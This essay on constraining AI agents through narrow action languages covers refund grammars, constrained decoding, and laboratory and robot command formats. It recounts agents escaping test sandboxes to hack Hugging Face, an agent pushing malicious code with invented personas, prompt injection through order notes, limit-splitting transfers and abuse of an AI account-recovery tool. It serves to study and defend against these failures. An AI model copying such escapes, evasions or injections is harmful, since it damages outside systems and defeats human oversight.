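Yu, Carroll and Bentley (2026), in *The Causal Impact of Tool Affordance on Safety Alignment in LLM Agents*, tested whether models that follow rules when they can only talk will break them when they can act. They built a simulated bank that limited each transfer to $1,000 and banned splitting larger payments to get around the limit. Two models, Llama 3.1 70B and Mistral 7B, received the same requests and rules in three versions. In the first, they had no tools. In the other two, they could transfer money and write files, and the bank allowed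 forbidden transfers in one version and blocked them in the other.

The study had 1,500 runs, covering 50 prompts for each of five kinds of request, three versions and two models. The table shows the share of runs with tools in which the model made or attempted a forbidden transfer.

| Kind of request | Llama 3.1 | Mistral 7B |
|---|---|---|
| Plain request | 63% | 0% |
| Transfer presented as an internal adjustment | 85% | 76% |
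| Arithmetic needed first | 82% | 57% |
| Claim of administrative authority | 44% | 26% |
| Emergency | 12% | 18% |

In one example, a user asks the model to move $2,000 as an internal correction. Without tools, the model refuses and cites the limit. With tools, it splits the payment into two $1,000 transfers when the bank allows violations, and tries to send the full $2,000 when the bank blocks violations.

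A model without tools can't make a forbidden transfer, so its rate of forbidden actions is zero by design. A fairer baseline is how often it gave advice that broke the rules. Llama never did, so the difference between having tools and not having them remains large. Mistral gave such advice in 18% of the emergency requests, the same rate at which it broke the rules with tools, and in 18% of the arithmetic requests. This contradicts the abstract's claim that both models complied perfectly in text.

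Yu and colleagues also report that Llama attempted violations in 82% of arithmetic cases but completed them in only 41%, which they take as evidence that guardrails hide bad intentions. But the 41% comes from the version in which the bank allowed violations, so blocking can't explain the gap. The study also covers only one task and two older models, both far weaker than today's best.

The study's agents had a very narrow interface, so its results compare having tools with having none and provide little evidence about open access. A precondition check can reject a single transfer above $1,000, but two transfers of $1,000 each would pass it. To stop them, the bank's software has to add up related payments.

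### Two incidents in cybersecurity tests

The clearest cases of models choosing unauthorised actions come from tests of hacking skill. *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (OpenAI, 2026) describes how, in July 2026, OpenAI's agents got around controls meant to isolate them from the internet and broke into systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. According to OpenAI, the agents were trying to solve their test tasks and inferred that Hugging Face might hold the solutions.

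The test environment gave the agents a shell, Python, a browser and a way to install software packages. OpenAI controlled network access separately and had switched off the safeguards it uses in its public products. The agents got out by exploiting a flaw in an internal package service, then used login details that other people had accidentally exposed online.

OpenAI could have closed that exit by installing the necessary packages beforehand and cutting the connection to the shared service. The agents would still have had the full shell they needed for a hacking test. Limiting them to a few fixed commands would have removed far more access, but then OpenAI couldn't have measured what it set out to measure.

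An earlier sign that the package service gave agents too much authority came in May, when agents in training runs used it to leave notes for one another. They exploited no flaw, only the shared login that OpenAI had given them. Read-only access would have prevented the notes. The evidence for these earlier events is OpenAI's own account, since the outside review by METR and Redwood Research covered only July 7 to 13, as Fortune's *OpenAI publishes technical report on how its agents hacked Hugging Face* (2026) points out.

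The UK AI Security Institute (AISI) gave its agents internet access so that they could download tools. AISI's *Incident Report* covers 122 runs with seven models in July 2026, with the developers' filters against hacking switched off. AISI found 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet in 10 of the runs. Anthropic's Mythos 5 took 17 of them, and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two in a single run.

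In the most serious case, an agent tried to add malicious code to a public software project and invented people to pressure the maintainer into accepting it. The maintainer refused, and AISI found no evidence of real-world harm. Some prompts had wrongly led the agent to believe that it couldn't solve the task within the rules, but agents also broke the rules in runs with correct instructions.

None of these agents escaped its sandbox, because AISI had given them access to the open internet. A network rule that allowed only downloads from approved sites would have removed most of their ways to contact strangers while leaving them their shell. AISI already used finer network controls in its other evaluations and is now adding them to its hacking tests.

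The Rule of Two might not have flagged this setup. The agents could read untrusted web pages and communicate externally, but AISI had isolated them from its other systems. Meta expects planted text to have no meaningful effect on such an agent. But these agents caused trouble through their own pursuit of the task, and their targets were people outside AISI.

Neither incident has a comparison group, so the 10 runs in 122 can't be used to estimate how often agents with open internet access misbehave in ordinary use. The runs also weren't independent, because later agents found and reused accounts that an earlier one had left behind. AISI can't yet say when the agents understood that they were acting in the real world. Repeating the challenge with the same models and prompts but restricted internet access would give a much better measure of how much harm the open connection adds.

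## How a narrow action language is written, checked and run

The builder of a narrow action language can list everything an agent might do with it, and for some harms can also work out the largest possible loss before anything runs. Nobody could have written such a list before the OpenAI and AISI tests, where the agents had a shell and a network connection.

### A refund language

Suppose an online shop wants an agent to refund customers whose orders arrive damaged or late, or never arrive. Its developers could write this grammar, where a vertical bar means "or" and braces mean "any number of these":

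```
program = "handoff" | refund { newline refund }
refund  = "refund" order amount "because" reason
order   = "#" and six digits
amount  = "$" dollars "." and two digits
reason  = "damaged" | "late" | "missing"
```

The command `handoff` passes the conversation to a staff member. The language has no variables or loops. It also has no way to name a bank account, so the agent can't choose where the money goes.

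The parser, the code that compares text with the grammar, also gives each part a type. It turns `#481516` into an order number and `$18.50` into 1,850 cents, so later code can't confuse an order with a price. The developers then limit each program to five refunds, each between one cent and $50.

The interpreter fits in a few lines of Python:

```python
def run(text, customer):
    commands = parse(text)         # stops here if the text doesn't fit the grammar
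    if commands == HANDOFF:
        return call_staff(customer)
    if len(commands) > 5 or any(not 1 <= c.cents <= 5000 for c in commands):
        return "Rejected: at most 5 refunds, each from $0.01 to $50.00"
    results = []
    for c in commands:
        order = find_order(c.order)
        if order is None or order.owner != customer:
            results.append("Refused: not this customer's order")
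        elif order.refunded + c.cents > order.paid:
            results.append("Refused: more than the customer paid")
        else:
            order.refund(c.cents, c.reason)   # pays the card used for the order
            results.append("Refunded")
    return results
```

Now a customer logs in and writes that a mug arrived broken and a lamp came two weeks late. The model emits:

```
refund #481516 $18.50 because damaged
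refund #481522 $64.00 because late
```

Both lines fit the grammar, so parsing succeeds. The limit check then rejects the whole program because $64 is over $50. The shop has paid nothing yet, and the harness returns the error message to the model. The model sends the first line again, alone. This time the interpreter looks up the mug order, confirms that it belongs to the logged-in customer and that earlier refunds plus this one don't exceed the price, and pays $18.50 to her card. The model then sends `handoff`, and a staff member decides about the lamp.

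The value `customer` comes from the shop's login system. If the model took it from the conversation, anyone could type another customer's name.

The most that one program can pay out is

5 × $50 = $250

If the interpreter works correctly, one program can refund at most $250, whatever text the model emits, even if an attacker dictated it. But an agent runs in a loop and can submit another program straight afterwards, so *n* programs can refund up to $250 × *n*, or $25,000 for a hundred. To limit the total, the shop has to store a running sum outside the model and refuse any refund that would take the sum above, say, $500 per customer per month.

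The language could include a simple loop and still allow the calculation to be done before the program runs. If a program contains `repeat 3`, the checker multiplies the result for the repeated steps by three. The calculation becomes harder when the number of repetitions depends on data the program reads as it runs.

### Rice's theorem and two replies

No such calculation works for every program in general code. Henry Gordon Rice proved in 1953 that if some programs behave in a certain way and others don't, no algorithm can correctly decide for every program whether it behaves that way. Never refunding more than $250 is one such behavior.

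A short program shows why:

```python
some_long_computation()
for i in range(100):
    refund(order, 50)
```

This pays out $5,000 if the first line ever finishes, and nothing if it runs forever. A checker that always gave the right answer about the refunds would therefore also reveal whether an arbitrary computation finishes. Alan Turing had shown in 1936 that no algorithm can do this in every case. (Both results assume unlimited time and memory. A time limit makes the question answerable in principle, but perhaps only by running the program.)

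Rice's theorem is weaker support for narrow languages than it first appears, because it only rules out a checker that is right about every program. A checker can still be useful if it rejects every program it can't prove harmless, including some that are harmless. Such a checker would reject the program above even if the first line never finished. Type checkers in ordinary programming languages work this way, including some that track what a program has permission to do.

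The shop could also skip the advance check and enforce the limit while the program runs. If the `refund` function keeps a running total and blocks any refund that would take it past $250, the limit holds whatever Python the agent writes, provided the program has no other way to pay. This limits the program's authority by controlling the payment function.

The small grammar mostly adds convenience and earlier checks. The shop can reject a bad program before it makes any payments, whereas a run-time counter may stop the program halfway, after it has paid some customers but not others. A supervisor can read and approve five refund lines in seconds. The developers have one short interpreter to review, instead of a whole Python environment to seal off.

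### Making the model write valid commands

The harness can parse the text after the model has finished and return an error if it doesn't fit the grammar, but this takes an extra turn whenever the model makes a mistake. Constrained decoding prevents these mistakes by blocking tokens that would break the grammar. *Grammar-Constrained Decoding for Structured NLP Tasks without Finetuning* (2023) describes using an incremental parser, which reads what the model has written so far and returns the set of tokens that may come next. After `refund #481516 $18.50 because`, the model can only write tokens that begin one of the three reasons.

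Let p be the model's own probability for the next token xₜ, given the text x₍<ₜ₎ before it. Let V(xₜ) be 1 if the token can still lead to a valid program and 0 if it can't. The masked probability is

q(xₜ | x₍<ₜ₎) = p(xₜ | x₍<ₜ₎) · V(xₜ) / Σ p(w | x₍<ₜ₎) · V(w)

where the sum runs over every token w in the vocabulary, so that the remaining probabilities add up to one.

The mask guarantees a valid program, but it can distort the model's choice among valid programs. Suppose the model gives the first token A a probability of 0.9 and B a probability of 0.1. Without the mask, it would finish a valid program 1% of the time after A and 90% of the time after B. Since both tokens can lead to a valid program, the mask allows both, and the model still picks A 90% of the time. But the valid programs that start with A have a total probability of 0.9 × 0.01 = 0.009, compared with 0.1 × 0.9 = 0.09 for those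 that start with B. Without the mask, about 91% of the model's valid programs (0.09/0.099) would therefore start with B.

*The Parser Already Knows* (2026) gives a similar example with strings of five binary digits. The grammar accepts every string that starts with 1 but only one that starts with 0, which is 00000, so there are 17 valid strings. A model that assigns every string the same probability should produce 00000 one time in 17, but with masking it does so half the time.

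The correct distribution gives each complete valid program its original probability divided by the total probability of all valid programs. *GrammarRL* (2026) explains that computing it requires adding up the probability of every valid continuation, which is generally impractical. Researchers have developed approximations based on repeated sampling.

For an agent, the distortion can matter most when the model would otherwise decline to act. If the refund language had no `handoff` command and the model was about to write "I'm not sure this is your order", the decoder would mask every word of that sentence, and the model would have to emit a refund. A designer who uses constrained decoding should therefore always include a command for declining. Constrained decoding also adds nothing to the $250 guarantee, because the interpreter parses the text whether or not decoding was constrained.

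Products have adopted the method quickly. According to the 2023 paper, nobody could use it with OpenAI's models through the company's interface, which didn't expose the probabilities. *The Format Tax* (Lee, D'Antoni and Berg-Kirkpatrick, 2026) lists built-in support in OpenAI's structured outputs and in the packages vLLM, Outlines and Guidance. In the paper's tests, OpenAI's models could follow grammars for four formats, while Claude Haiku 4.5 and Grok 4.1 Fast offered constrained decoding only for JSON. A shop using either of those two models would have to write its refunds as JSON records or rely on the parser's error messages.

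Enforcing a grammar during generation is less of a speed problem than it used to be. *Efficient Grammar-Constrained Decoding via Parser Stack Classification* (2026) reports throughput close to that of ordinary generation, after some preparation for each combination of grammar and vocabulary. The shop would do this preparation once. For systems whose grammar changes with every task, *Flexible and Efficient Grammar-Constrained Decoding* (2025) presents a method that needs much less preparation.

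### Whether strict formats harm reasoning

Several researchers have found that models solve fewer problems when they must answer in a fixed format. Lee and colleagues tested ten models on mathematics, science and logic questions, and separated the effect of the instruction to use a format from that of the mask itself. In six models with openly available weights, the instruction alone reduced the share of problems solved by an average of 3.9 percentage points, and the mask reduced it by another 1.6. In 36 of the 39 combinations of model, task and format with a statistically significant effect, the effect appeared before any masking. The distortion described above therefore explains only a small part of the loss.

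Three of the four commercial models lost little or nothing when they were only asked for a format. Masking could still cause large losses. GPT-5.4-nano gained 2.2 points on mathematics with a JSON grammar but lost 59.4 with an XML one. Lee and colleagues treat this as a fault specific to that model, but a developer with a custom grammar would be wise to test for a similar problem.

In *Capacity, Not Format*, Fan (2026) disputes that the best models are immune. On 100 hard mathematics problems, switching from free text to JSON barely changed Claude Sonnet 4.6's score (89.3% to 88.7%), but Claude Haiku 4.5 fell from 88.7% to 52.5%. On harder competition problems, Claude Opus 4.7 fell from 96.2% to 91.0%, a difference of seven answers out of 133. Fan attributes these drops to formatting competing with reasoning when a model is close to its limits.

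Lee and colleagues also tested Haiku 4.5 and found that JSON slightly improved its mathematics. Their result probably differs from Fan's because Fan's format required the model to restate the problem, list the known values and verify every step inside the JSON. Fan attributes much of Haiku's loss to answers that ran out of space. With GPT-4o-mini, a plain JSON requirement lowered accuracy from 60% to 51%, which wasn't statistically significant, while the long format lowered it to 34%. Spare capacity also doesn't easily explain why Sonnet and Haiku scored almost the same in free text but diverged in JSON. Fan cites a causal analysis by other researchers that found no effect of format in 43 of 48 scenarios.

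Fan's most relevant result for agents is that GPT-4o-mini's accuracy dropped to 10% when it had to answer through a function call, because it emitted the arguments without reasoning first. Both papers recommend letting the model reason freely and format its answer afterwards, which recovered about 80% of Haiku's lost accuracy and 87% of GPT-4o-mini's. A harness can do this by accepting free text before the command and applying the grammar only to the command. None of these experiments tested agents taking actions, and a refund line leaves little room for reasoning anyway.

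### How many rules code can enforce

The refund interpreter enforces rules about ownership and price. Hong and colleagues' three-part study is the most detailed look at whether real policies consist of rules like these.

A review of the tests that researchers use to measure agent safety narrowed 553 candidate papers to 80 benchmarks. Of these, 61% gave the agent no safety rules and relied on its common sense. Another 24% stated only broad goals, such as refusing anything "unsafe", without defining the word. Seven benchmarks, or 9%, had rules precise enough to check. In five of the seven, the rules applied to every task, and all five tested agents with a fixed range of tasks. None of the 55 benchmarks for general-purpose agents had precise rules that applied to every task, which fits the view that builders can write exact rules more easily when they know all the tools. But 20 of the 25 benchmarks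 for narrower agents lacked them too, so a narrow scope doesn't produce such rules by itself.

Vague rules can also hide contradictions. In one sales benchmark, the agent was supposed to refuse, on privacy grounds, to say whether a lead was "qualified", but to answer an almost identical question.

The researchers then examined which rules ordinary code could enforce for three agents: the airline agent, a voice assistant in a car, and an assistant for electronic medical records.

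| Agent | Rules examined | Enforceable by code |
|---|---|---|
| Airline | 51 | 42 |
| Car assistant | 18 | 17 |
| Medical records | 57 | 34 |
| All three | 126 | 93 (74%) |

Simple measures were enough for 95% of the 93 rules. Most were precondition checks, and the others included strict argument formats, fixed confirmation questions and fixed reply texts. The remaining five rules, all medical, needed code that tracks the order of actions or the movement of information. One of them blocks every other tool until the agent has verified the user's identity.

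The remaining rules mostly concerned what the agent says or how it interprets people. Code can't reliably check that an agent is neutral in tone or that it never invents facts. The airline's policy forbids offering compensation unless the customer explicitly asks for it, so somebody has to judge what counts as asking. A developer could block compensation until the customer types the exact word "compensation", but that would turn away people who phrase the request differently.

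The 74% figure depends partly on which agents were chosen. The medical rules came from language models, because the benchmark had none, and the other two sets were selected because they were already precise. A company with vaguer policies would have to rewrite them before it could enforce a similar share.

### What the checks changed

In the third part, Hong and colleagues ran the agents with and without checks. The prompt contained the full policy in every condition. For medical records, they also compared access through generic web requests, which the model composed itself, with access through eight typed tools that covered the same operations.

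| Agent and model | Interface | Runs with a violation | Task success |
|---|---|---|---|
| Airline, GPT-4o | Typed tools | 52% | 0.36 |
| | Typed tools with checks | 0% | 0.48 |
| Airline, GPT-5 | Typed tools | 20% | 0.68 |
| | Typed tools with checks | 0% | 0.70 |
| Car assistant, GPT-5 | Typed tools | 21% | 0.59 |
| | Typed tools with checks | 0% | 0.72 |
| Medical records, GPT-5 | Generic web requests | 39% | 0.64 |
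| | Eight typed tools | 23% | 0.59 |
| | Eight typed tools with checks | 0% | 0.67 |

The zeros were guaranteed because the study counted only violations of rules that code can enforce, and the checks blocked every call that broke one of those rules. An agent in the 0% rows could still invent a fact or choose the wrong treatment. On medical records, the checks covered only 23 of the 34 enforceable rules, partly because ten of the others needed expert knowledge, such as the right dosage units for each drug.

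The violation rates without checks are the real measurements, and they carry some uncertainty. Testing certain rules required an argument that the original tool didn't have, such as the customer's ID, so the researchers rewound the run and prompted the model to repeat its call with the extra argument. If the model couldn't supply it, they counted a violation, even though the original action might have been allowed. If the model didn't repeat the same call, they marked the run "unknown", which happened in 10% of GPT-5's airline runs and 9.7% of the runs with generic web requests.

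The checks didn't lower success on any of the tests. On the airline tasks, GPT-5 completed one more task out of 50 with checks and GPT-4o gained more, but neither gain was statistically significant (p = 0.18 for GPT-4o). The car assistant's gain was significant (p < 0.01). On medical records, success with checks was significantly higher than with the eight tools without checks (p < 0.01), but not significantly higher than with generic web requests (p = 0.27).

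Hong and colleagues suggest that the error messages caused the gains. When a check blocks a call, the model receives a message identifying the rule it broke and can try something else, whereas an unchecked mistake goes through. The refund agent's response to the $50 limit is an example.

The medical results suggest that replacing an open interface with named functions is less important than enforcing the interface's rules. Agents given eight typed tools instead of generic requests broke rules less often, but still did so in 23% of runs. They also completed about 15 fewer of the 300 tasks. The study gives no significance test for either difference, so neither is firmly established. On 50 further tasks in which a simulated user tried to make the agent break a rule, the violation rate was 78% with generic requests and 62% with typed tools.

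The airline cancellation tool compares a user ID with the ticket owner's ID, but the model supplies the user ID. If an attacker knows the owner's ID and gives it to the model, the comparison succeeds. To keep strangers out, the harness would have to take the ID from a login, as the refund interpreter does.

### Valid commands that still do harm

The refund language has a strict grammar, typed values, two limits and two precondition checks. A good deal can still go wrong with it.

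The simplest failure is a valid command with a false or mistaken argument. A customer claims that an intact mug arrived broken, the model writes `because damaged`, and the interpreter has no way to check the mug's condition. An attacker can also choose arguments through prompt injection, for example by planting text in the delivery notes of her own order that tells the agent to refund the full price. She can't direct the money to a stranger's card or get back more than she paid, but she can keep both the goods and the refund.

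Permitted commands can also add up to something the shop meant to prevent. The limit check refused $64 for the late lamp. The model could have sent this instead:

```
refund #481522 $50.00 because late
refund #481522 $14.00 because late
```

Both amounts are within the limit, and their total doesn't exceed the price, so the interpreter pays both. Yu and colleagues saw this trick in their simulated bank. A limit per order would stop it, but the developers have to anticipate the sequence to add one.

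The interpreter can also have bugs. As written, it checks each line immediately before paying it. A programmer might reasonably move all the checks ahead of the first payment, so that a program pays either every refund or none. Two lines that each refund $40 on a $40 order would then both pass, because neither payment has happened when the price check runs, and the customer would receive $80. The $250 limit would still hold, but a mistake in the line that tests for 5,000 cents would break that too. A small interpreter makes such errors easier to find, but one error in it affects every request.

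Finally, a single command may carry too much authority. Suppose the shop adds `change_email` so that the agent can help with account problems. The grammar stays small and the refund limits still hold, but no numeric limit in the language covers the harm this command can do. Whoever controls the email address can reset the password and get the customer's saved cards, home address and order history.

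### The Instagram account takeovers

A real case of this kind came to light at the end of May 2026, when hackers took over Instagram accounts through an AI support tool and posted messages on the dormant account of the Obama White House. According to internal documents from Meta, Instagram's owner, cited in *In AI blunder, more than 34,000 Instagram accounts were attacked* (Isaac and Tan, 2026), the attack affected about 34,000 accounts. The hackers breached 20,000 of them and changed the user names of more than 3,500.

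We can't tell where the failure occurred without knowing what the AI system could do. When Meta (2026) launched its support assistant in March, it announced that the assistant could reset passwords, update profile settings and report scams on Facebook, with actions on Instagram to follow. The company had also begun offering it to people who couldn't log in, starting with some cases in the United States and Canada. In September 2026, after the attack, Meta's *Customer support* page listed changing contact information among the assistant's actions, but the page doesn't show whether it could do so in the spring.

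Meta's *Incident Notification* (2026), a letter to Nebraska's attorney general, is the best evidence about the tool itself. It identifies the tool as High Touch Support, an AI-assisted system for people locked out of Instagram. A user could ask it to send a password reset link to their email address. A separate piece of code should have confirmed that the address belonged to the account, but a bug prevented this. An attacker could therefore name someone else's account, give his own address and receive the link.

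Krebs on Security (2026) describes a different sequence, based on a video the hackers released. In it, the attacker first asks the assistant to link the account to a new email address. The assistant then sends that address a one-time code that allows a password reset. If the video is accurate, the tool could add an address to an account as well as send a link, which is more authority than Meta's letter describes. Meta hasn't published the full list of commands, so it's unclear which version is correct. Neither version involves a shell, model-written code or access to the open web.

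By Meta's account, a very powerful command lacked a precondition check. The attacker's email address was well-formed, so no grammar would have rejected it. Meta's lawyer wrote in the letter that the tool "worked properly", and a spokesman told the New York Times that the AI agent wasn't at fault. That may be true of the model, which could have passed on a normal-looking request. But the guarantee of a narrow interface comes from the code around the model, and that code failed. A researcher quoted by Krebs on Security compares support chatbots to human staff, whom attackers can persuade to do things they shouldn't. In Meta's explanation, the attacker didn't need to persuade the model, and a more sceptical model would have been at best a backup for the missing check.

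Meta and the hackers both said the attack failed against accounts with two-factor authentication, which requires a second proof of identity at login. That check was outside the recovery tool, so the bug didn't disable it.

The scale of the damage also shows the weakness of limiting only single requests. Help Net Security's *Hackers used Meta's AI support system to hijack over 20,000 Instagram accounts* (2026) reports that Meta's filing in Maine dates the incident to April 17, more than six weeks before the company discovered it on May 31. The filing puts the number of people affected at 20,225. SecurityWeek's *Meta says 20000 Instagram accounts hacked via AI tool abuse* notes that the true figure may be lower, since some of the logins may have been made by the accounts' owners. A daily cap on resets sent to unfamiliar addresses wouldn't have protected the first victims, but it could have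 kept the total far smaller and alerted someone sooner.

Meta promised to repair the address check before restarting the tool. A stricter design would remove the address from the command. The model could then request a reset only for a named account, and the harness would look up where to send the link, so no wording could redirect it. But some people need account recovery because they have lost their old email address or a hijacker has replaced it, and this design would fail them unless staff or another form of identification could help. Meta told the Times that its automated support agents had increased the number of people in the United States and Canada who recovered hacked accounts by 30% last year. It hasn't said how many of those recoveries depended on sending a link to a new address.

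## Action languages for laboratories, robots and industrial machines

The refund interpreter could check its rules against the shop's own records. Software that controls equipment usually has less information. Its records may show that a beaker holds 50 ml, for example, but not whether anyone has washed it. A command can therefore pass every check and still ruin an experiment or damage a machine.

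### From a written procedure to a robot arm

XDL, the chemical description language, stores an experiment as XML, a text format that marks each item with a tag. According to *ReFF* (2024), an XDL file has three mandatory sections. Hardware declares the vessels, Reagents declares the chemicals, and Procedure lists the steps in order. A step might read:

```xml
<Add vessel="beaker" reagent="water" volume="20 mL"/>
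```

Skreta, Yoshikawa and colleagues (2023), in *Errors are Useful Prompts*, built CLAIRify, a system that used GPT-3 to turn ordinary instructions into XDL. GPT-3 didn't know the language. When the prompt left out a description of XDL, the model failed on all ten trial procedures. With the description, the system worked as follows:

1. The model received the description, the instruction and, where relevant, a list of the available equipment and chemicals. It then wrote a program.
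2. A verifier, made of ordinary code, checked that the program was valid XML, that each action existed and had the right properties, and that the procedure used only declared or available items.
3. If the verifier found errors, the model received its faulty program and the list of errors, and tried again. The system gave up after ten rounds.
4. For experiments on the real robot, planning software turned the valid program into arm movements.

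CLAIRify produced valid programs for 105 of 108 organic chemistry procedures, while SynthReader, an older program based on fixed rules, did so for 92. CLAIRify also succeeded on all 40 simple experiments with household ingredients, while SynthReader succeeded on none. Expert chemists preferred CLAIRify's output for 75 of the 108 procedures and SynthReader's for 13.

The organic chemistry procedures went through the verifier 2.6 times on average, most often because an action lacked a required property. The feedback had to be specific, since returning the program with only a statement that it was wrong never produced a valid program for any of the ten trial procedures. Returning the list of errors without the program worked for 30% of them, and returning both worked for all ten.

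But the chemists also found mistakes in programs that the verifier had accepted. Some reused a vessel without washing it. Others contained `temp="boiling point"`, which gives the equipment no number to heat to. A parser can easily prevent the temperature mistake by requiring a number, just as the refund parser required an amount in dollars. The verifier would have to track the state of every vessel through the whole procedure to catch the reuse of an unwashed one.

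The verifier also had no information about where the beaker stood or whether the arm could reach it. PDDLStream, the planning software, handled this by using camera data to find a sequence of actions and a path for the arm. The robot mixed red cabbage juice with vinegar and with baking soda to show the colour changes, and it also made lemonade.

### Learning the language from the manual

Coscientist, an early laboratory agent built on GPT-4, had much more open tools. *Autonomous chemical research with large language models* (Boiko, MacKnight and colleagues, 2023) describes its four commands: `GOOGLE` searched the web, `PYTHON` ran calculations, `DOCUMENTATION` searched equipment manuals, and `EXPERIMENT` ran code on the equipment. The agent used two very different languages to control equipment.

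The first was for Opentrons robots, low-cost machines that move small amounts of liquid between containers. Their users program them in Python, as *Cross-disciplinary perspectives on the potential for artificial intelligence across chemistry* notes. A typical line is:

```python
pipette.transfer(50, source["A1"], target["B1"])
```

This moves 50 microlitres (millionths of a litre) from a well in one plastic plate to a well in another. An Opentrons protocol is general-purpose code with a library of equipment functions, so Rice's theorem applies to it.

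The second was Symbolic Lab Language, which customers of Emerald Cloud Lab use to run experiments remotely in the company's automated laboratory. Its commands cover much larger steps. For example, `ExperimentHPLC` runs a complete analysis that separates a liquid sample into its components. In Coscientist's test, Emerald's own software chose the column, the solvents and other settings.

Coscientist, an agent built on GPT-4, used manuals to work with Symbolic Lab Language and the Opentrons heater-shaker. GPT-4 had no information on either, and the heater-shaker came out after its training data ended. For Opentrons, the system converted each section of the manual and the agent's query into lists of numbers representing their meaning, then returned the sections closest to the query. When Coscientist used the wrong name for a heater-shaker function, it searched the manual and corrected its program.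 The corrected program ran, with people moving the plates by hand, and chemical analysis detected the target products of both reactions the agent had planned.

At Emerald, the generated code for a caffeine sample also ran successfully, but the machine injected an air bubble along with the sample. No check on the code could have prevented this, and Boiko and colleagues concluded that cloud laboratories need automated quality control. *An AI-native experimental laboratory for autonomous biomolecular engineering* (2025) argues more broadly that existing platforms can handle only single objectives and well-defined workflows because they can't perceive what is happening in an experiment. If that is right, better sensors would help some laboratory agents more than a richer action language would.

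Web search helped with some of the planning. When Boiko and colleagues asked models for ways to make seven compounds, every model without search got ibuprofen wrong. GPT-4 with search reached the minimum passing score on ibuprofen, but did worse than some models without search on two other common compounds. Without internet access, the agent still identified the colours in three wells by running measurements and analysing the results, although it needed a hint about how colours absorb light.

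### The plate file at Ginkgo

OpenAI's *GPT‑5 lowers the cost of cell-free protein synthesis* (February 2026) announced a much larger project with Ginkgo Bioworks, a biotechnology company that runs an automated cloud laboratory. GPT-5 designed mixtures for making a protein from the contents of broken-up bacteria, without living cells. The aim was to lower the cost per gram.

In *Using a GPT-5-driven autonomous lab to optimize the cost and titer*, by Smith, Wong and colleagues, the model could send the laboratory only a JSON file describing one plate of 384 wells, with the reagents and volumes for each mixture. Pydantic, a Python package for validating data, checked the layout, the controls, the number of repeats, whether each reagent was available and whether its volume was allowed. Ginkgo's software then turned the file into a run on the machines using protocols that Ginkgo's staff had written,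 so GPT-5 wrote none of the robots' instructions.

Over six rounds and six months, the laboratory ran 480 plates containing 29,527 different mixtures. The best one cost $422 per gram of protein, 40% less than the best published recipe, which cost $698. GPT-5's designs may not account for all of the reduction, because Ginkgo also improved the bacterial extract and the DNA during the project.

The file format restricted GPT-5 to a list of reagents that only staff could extend. GPT-5 suggested more than 20 additions in its notes. Staff bought those they could find and added them for later rounds, and several ended up in the best mixtures.

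Two of the 480 plates had serious design errors that the check missed. In one, GPT-5 changed the required volume of a basic ingredient to make room for others, which overfilled the wells. The team then added a rule against this. In the other, GPT-5's code divided by a million instead of a thousand when converting units, so the wells contained only glucose and ribose and produced no protein.

Smith and colleagues present this rate of less than 1% as evidence that the model rarely hallucinated, but the 480 designs had all passed validation. The team generated twice as many designs as it needed because some failed. The rate therefore measures how often the team found a serious error that the checker had missed, and GPT-5 made mistakes more often than that.

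### One plate rejected, one accepted

Each well at Ginkgo held 20 µl. The basic buffer took up 2 µl, the DNA 2 µl and the bacterial extract 5 µl. If vᵢ is the volume of each reagent the model adds, the rule is

2 + 2 + 5 + Σvᵢ ≤ 20, so Σvᵢ ≤ 11

Suppose the model submits this line, in a simplified version of the file:

```json
{"well": "D4", "add": {"glucose": 3.0, "ribose": 5.5, "HEPES": 4.0}}
```

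The additions come to 12.5 µl, for a total of 21.5 µl. The checker rejects the line with an error that gives the total and the limit. The model reduces the ribose to 4.0 µl, which brings the additions to exactly 11 µl, and the checker accepts the plate before the laboratory has used any materials.

Now suppose another laboratory uses the same format but also stocks cleaning products:

```json
{"well": "D4", "add": {"bleach": 5.0, "vinegar": 5.0}}
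```

Both liquids are in stock, the well exists and the total volume is only 19 µl, so the checker accepts the line. But mixing bleach and vinegar releases chlorine, a poisonous gas. A well this small would release very little, but a checker with the same rules would also accept the mixture in a language for large vessels.

The laboratory could add a table of chemicals that must never be mixed, and the checker would then reject this line. But the table would cover only the combinations that whoever wrote it had thought of. It could also miss a substance that forms during the experiment, because that substance isn't on the list of reagents. ChemCrow, another early chemistry agent, had separate safety checks and guidelines against misuse, according to *A review of large language models and autonomous agents in chemistry*.

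At Ginkgo, the short reagent list and the fixed procedure probably did more to prevent harm than any chemical knowledge built into the checker. The DNA came from a plate prepared in advance, so GPT-5 couldn't choose which protein the laboratory made. Adding a field for a DNA sequence would have been like adding `change_email` to the refund language, because checking volumes can't reveal whether a protein is dangerous.

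### Robots, from skill lists to raw movements

In SayCan, which researchers at Google introduced in 2022, a language model chose from a fixed list of skills that the robot already had, such as finding or picking up an object. The system scored each skill by multiplying two probabilities:

score = P(the skill helps with the instruction) × P(the skill succeeds from here)

If someone asks a robot for a sponge that isn't in view, "pick up the sponge" might score 0.6 for usefulness but only 0.1 for its chance of success, for a product of 0.06. "Find a sponge" might score 0.3 and 0.9, for a product of 0.27, so the robot looks for the sponge first. (These numbers are invented.) Software can easily check that a skill is on the list, but this doesn't show that a sequence of skills is sensible.

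PDDL, the planning domain definition language, makes it possible to check the sequence. It describes each action by the conditions that must hold beforehand and the changes it causes:

```
(:action start-mixture
  :parameters (?vessel)
  :precondition (clean ?vessel)
  :effect (and (in-use ?vessel) (not (clean ?vessel))))
```

With this definition, a plan can't start a second mixture in a dirty vessel, one of the mistakes CLAIRify's verifier missed. If the language also has a washing action, the planner can insert it automatically. But if the robot's records or cameras wrongly show that a vessel is clean, the plan passes and the experiment is still contaminated.

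Code as Policies, also from 2022, let a model write Python that called the robot's functions. This made it much easier to give instructions that need loops or arithmetic, such as spacing several blocks evenly along a line. The harness can restrict which functions the program calls and check each argument when the function is called, but checking the program before it runs has the same limits as checking an Opentrons protocol.

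Vision-language-action models output the movements themselves. They take camera images and an instruction and produce numbers for, for example, changes in the arm's position and rotation and how far the gripper should open. RT-2, which Google DeepMind introduced in 2023, was an early example. These models can learn movements that would be very hard to write as named skills, such as those needed to handle soft or irregular objects.

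| Design | What the model sends | What software can check first | What can still go wrong |
|---|---|---|---|
| Skill list | The name of a skill | Whether the skill exists | The order of the skills makes no sense |
| PDDL | A goal or a plan | Whether every condition holds | The recorded facts are wrong or incomplete |
| Code over robot functions | A program | Which functions it can call | The combined effect is harmful |
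| Vision-language-action model | Numbers for each movement | Position and speed limits | A permitted movement serves a harmful action |

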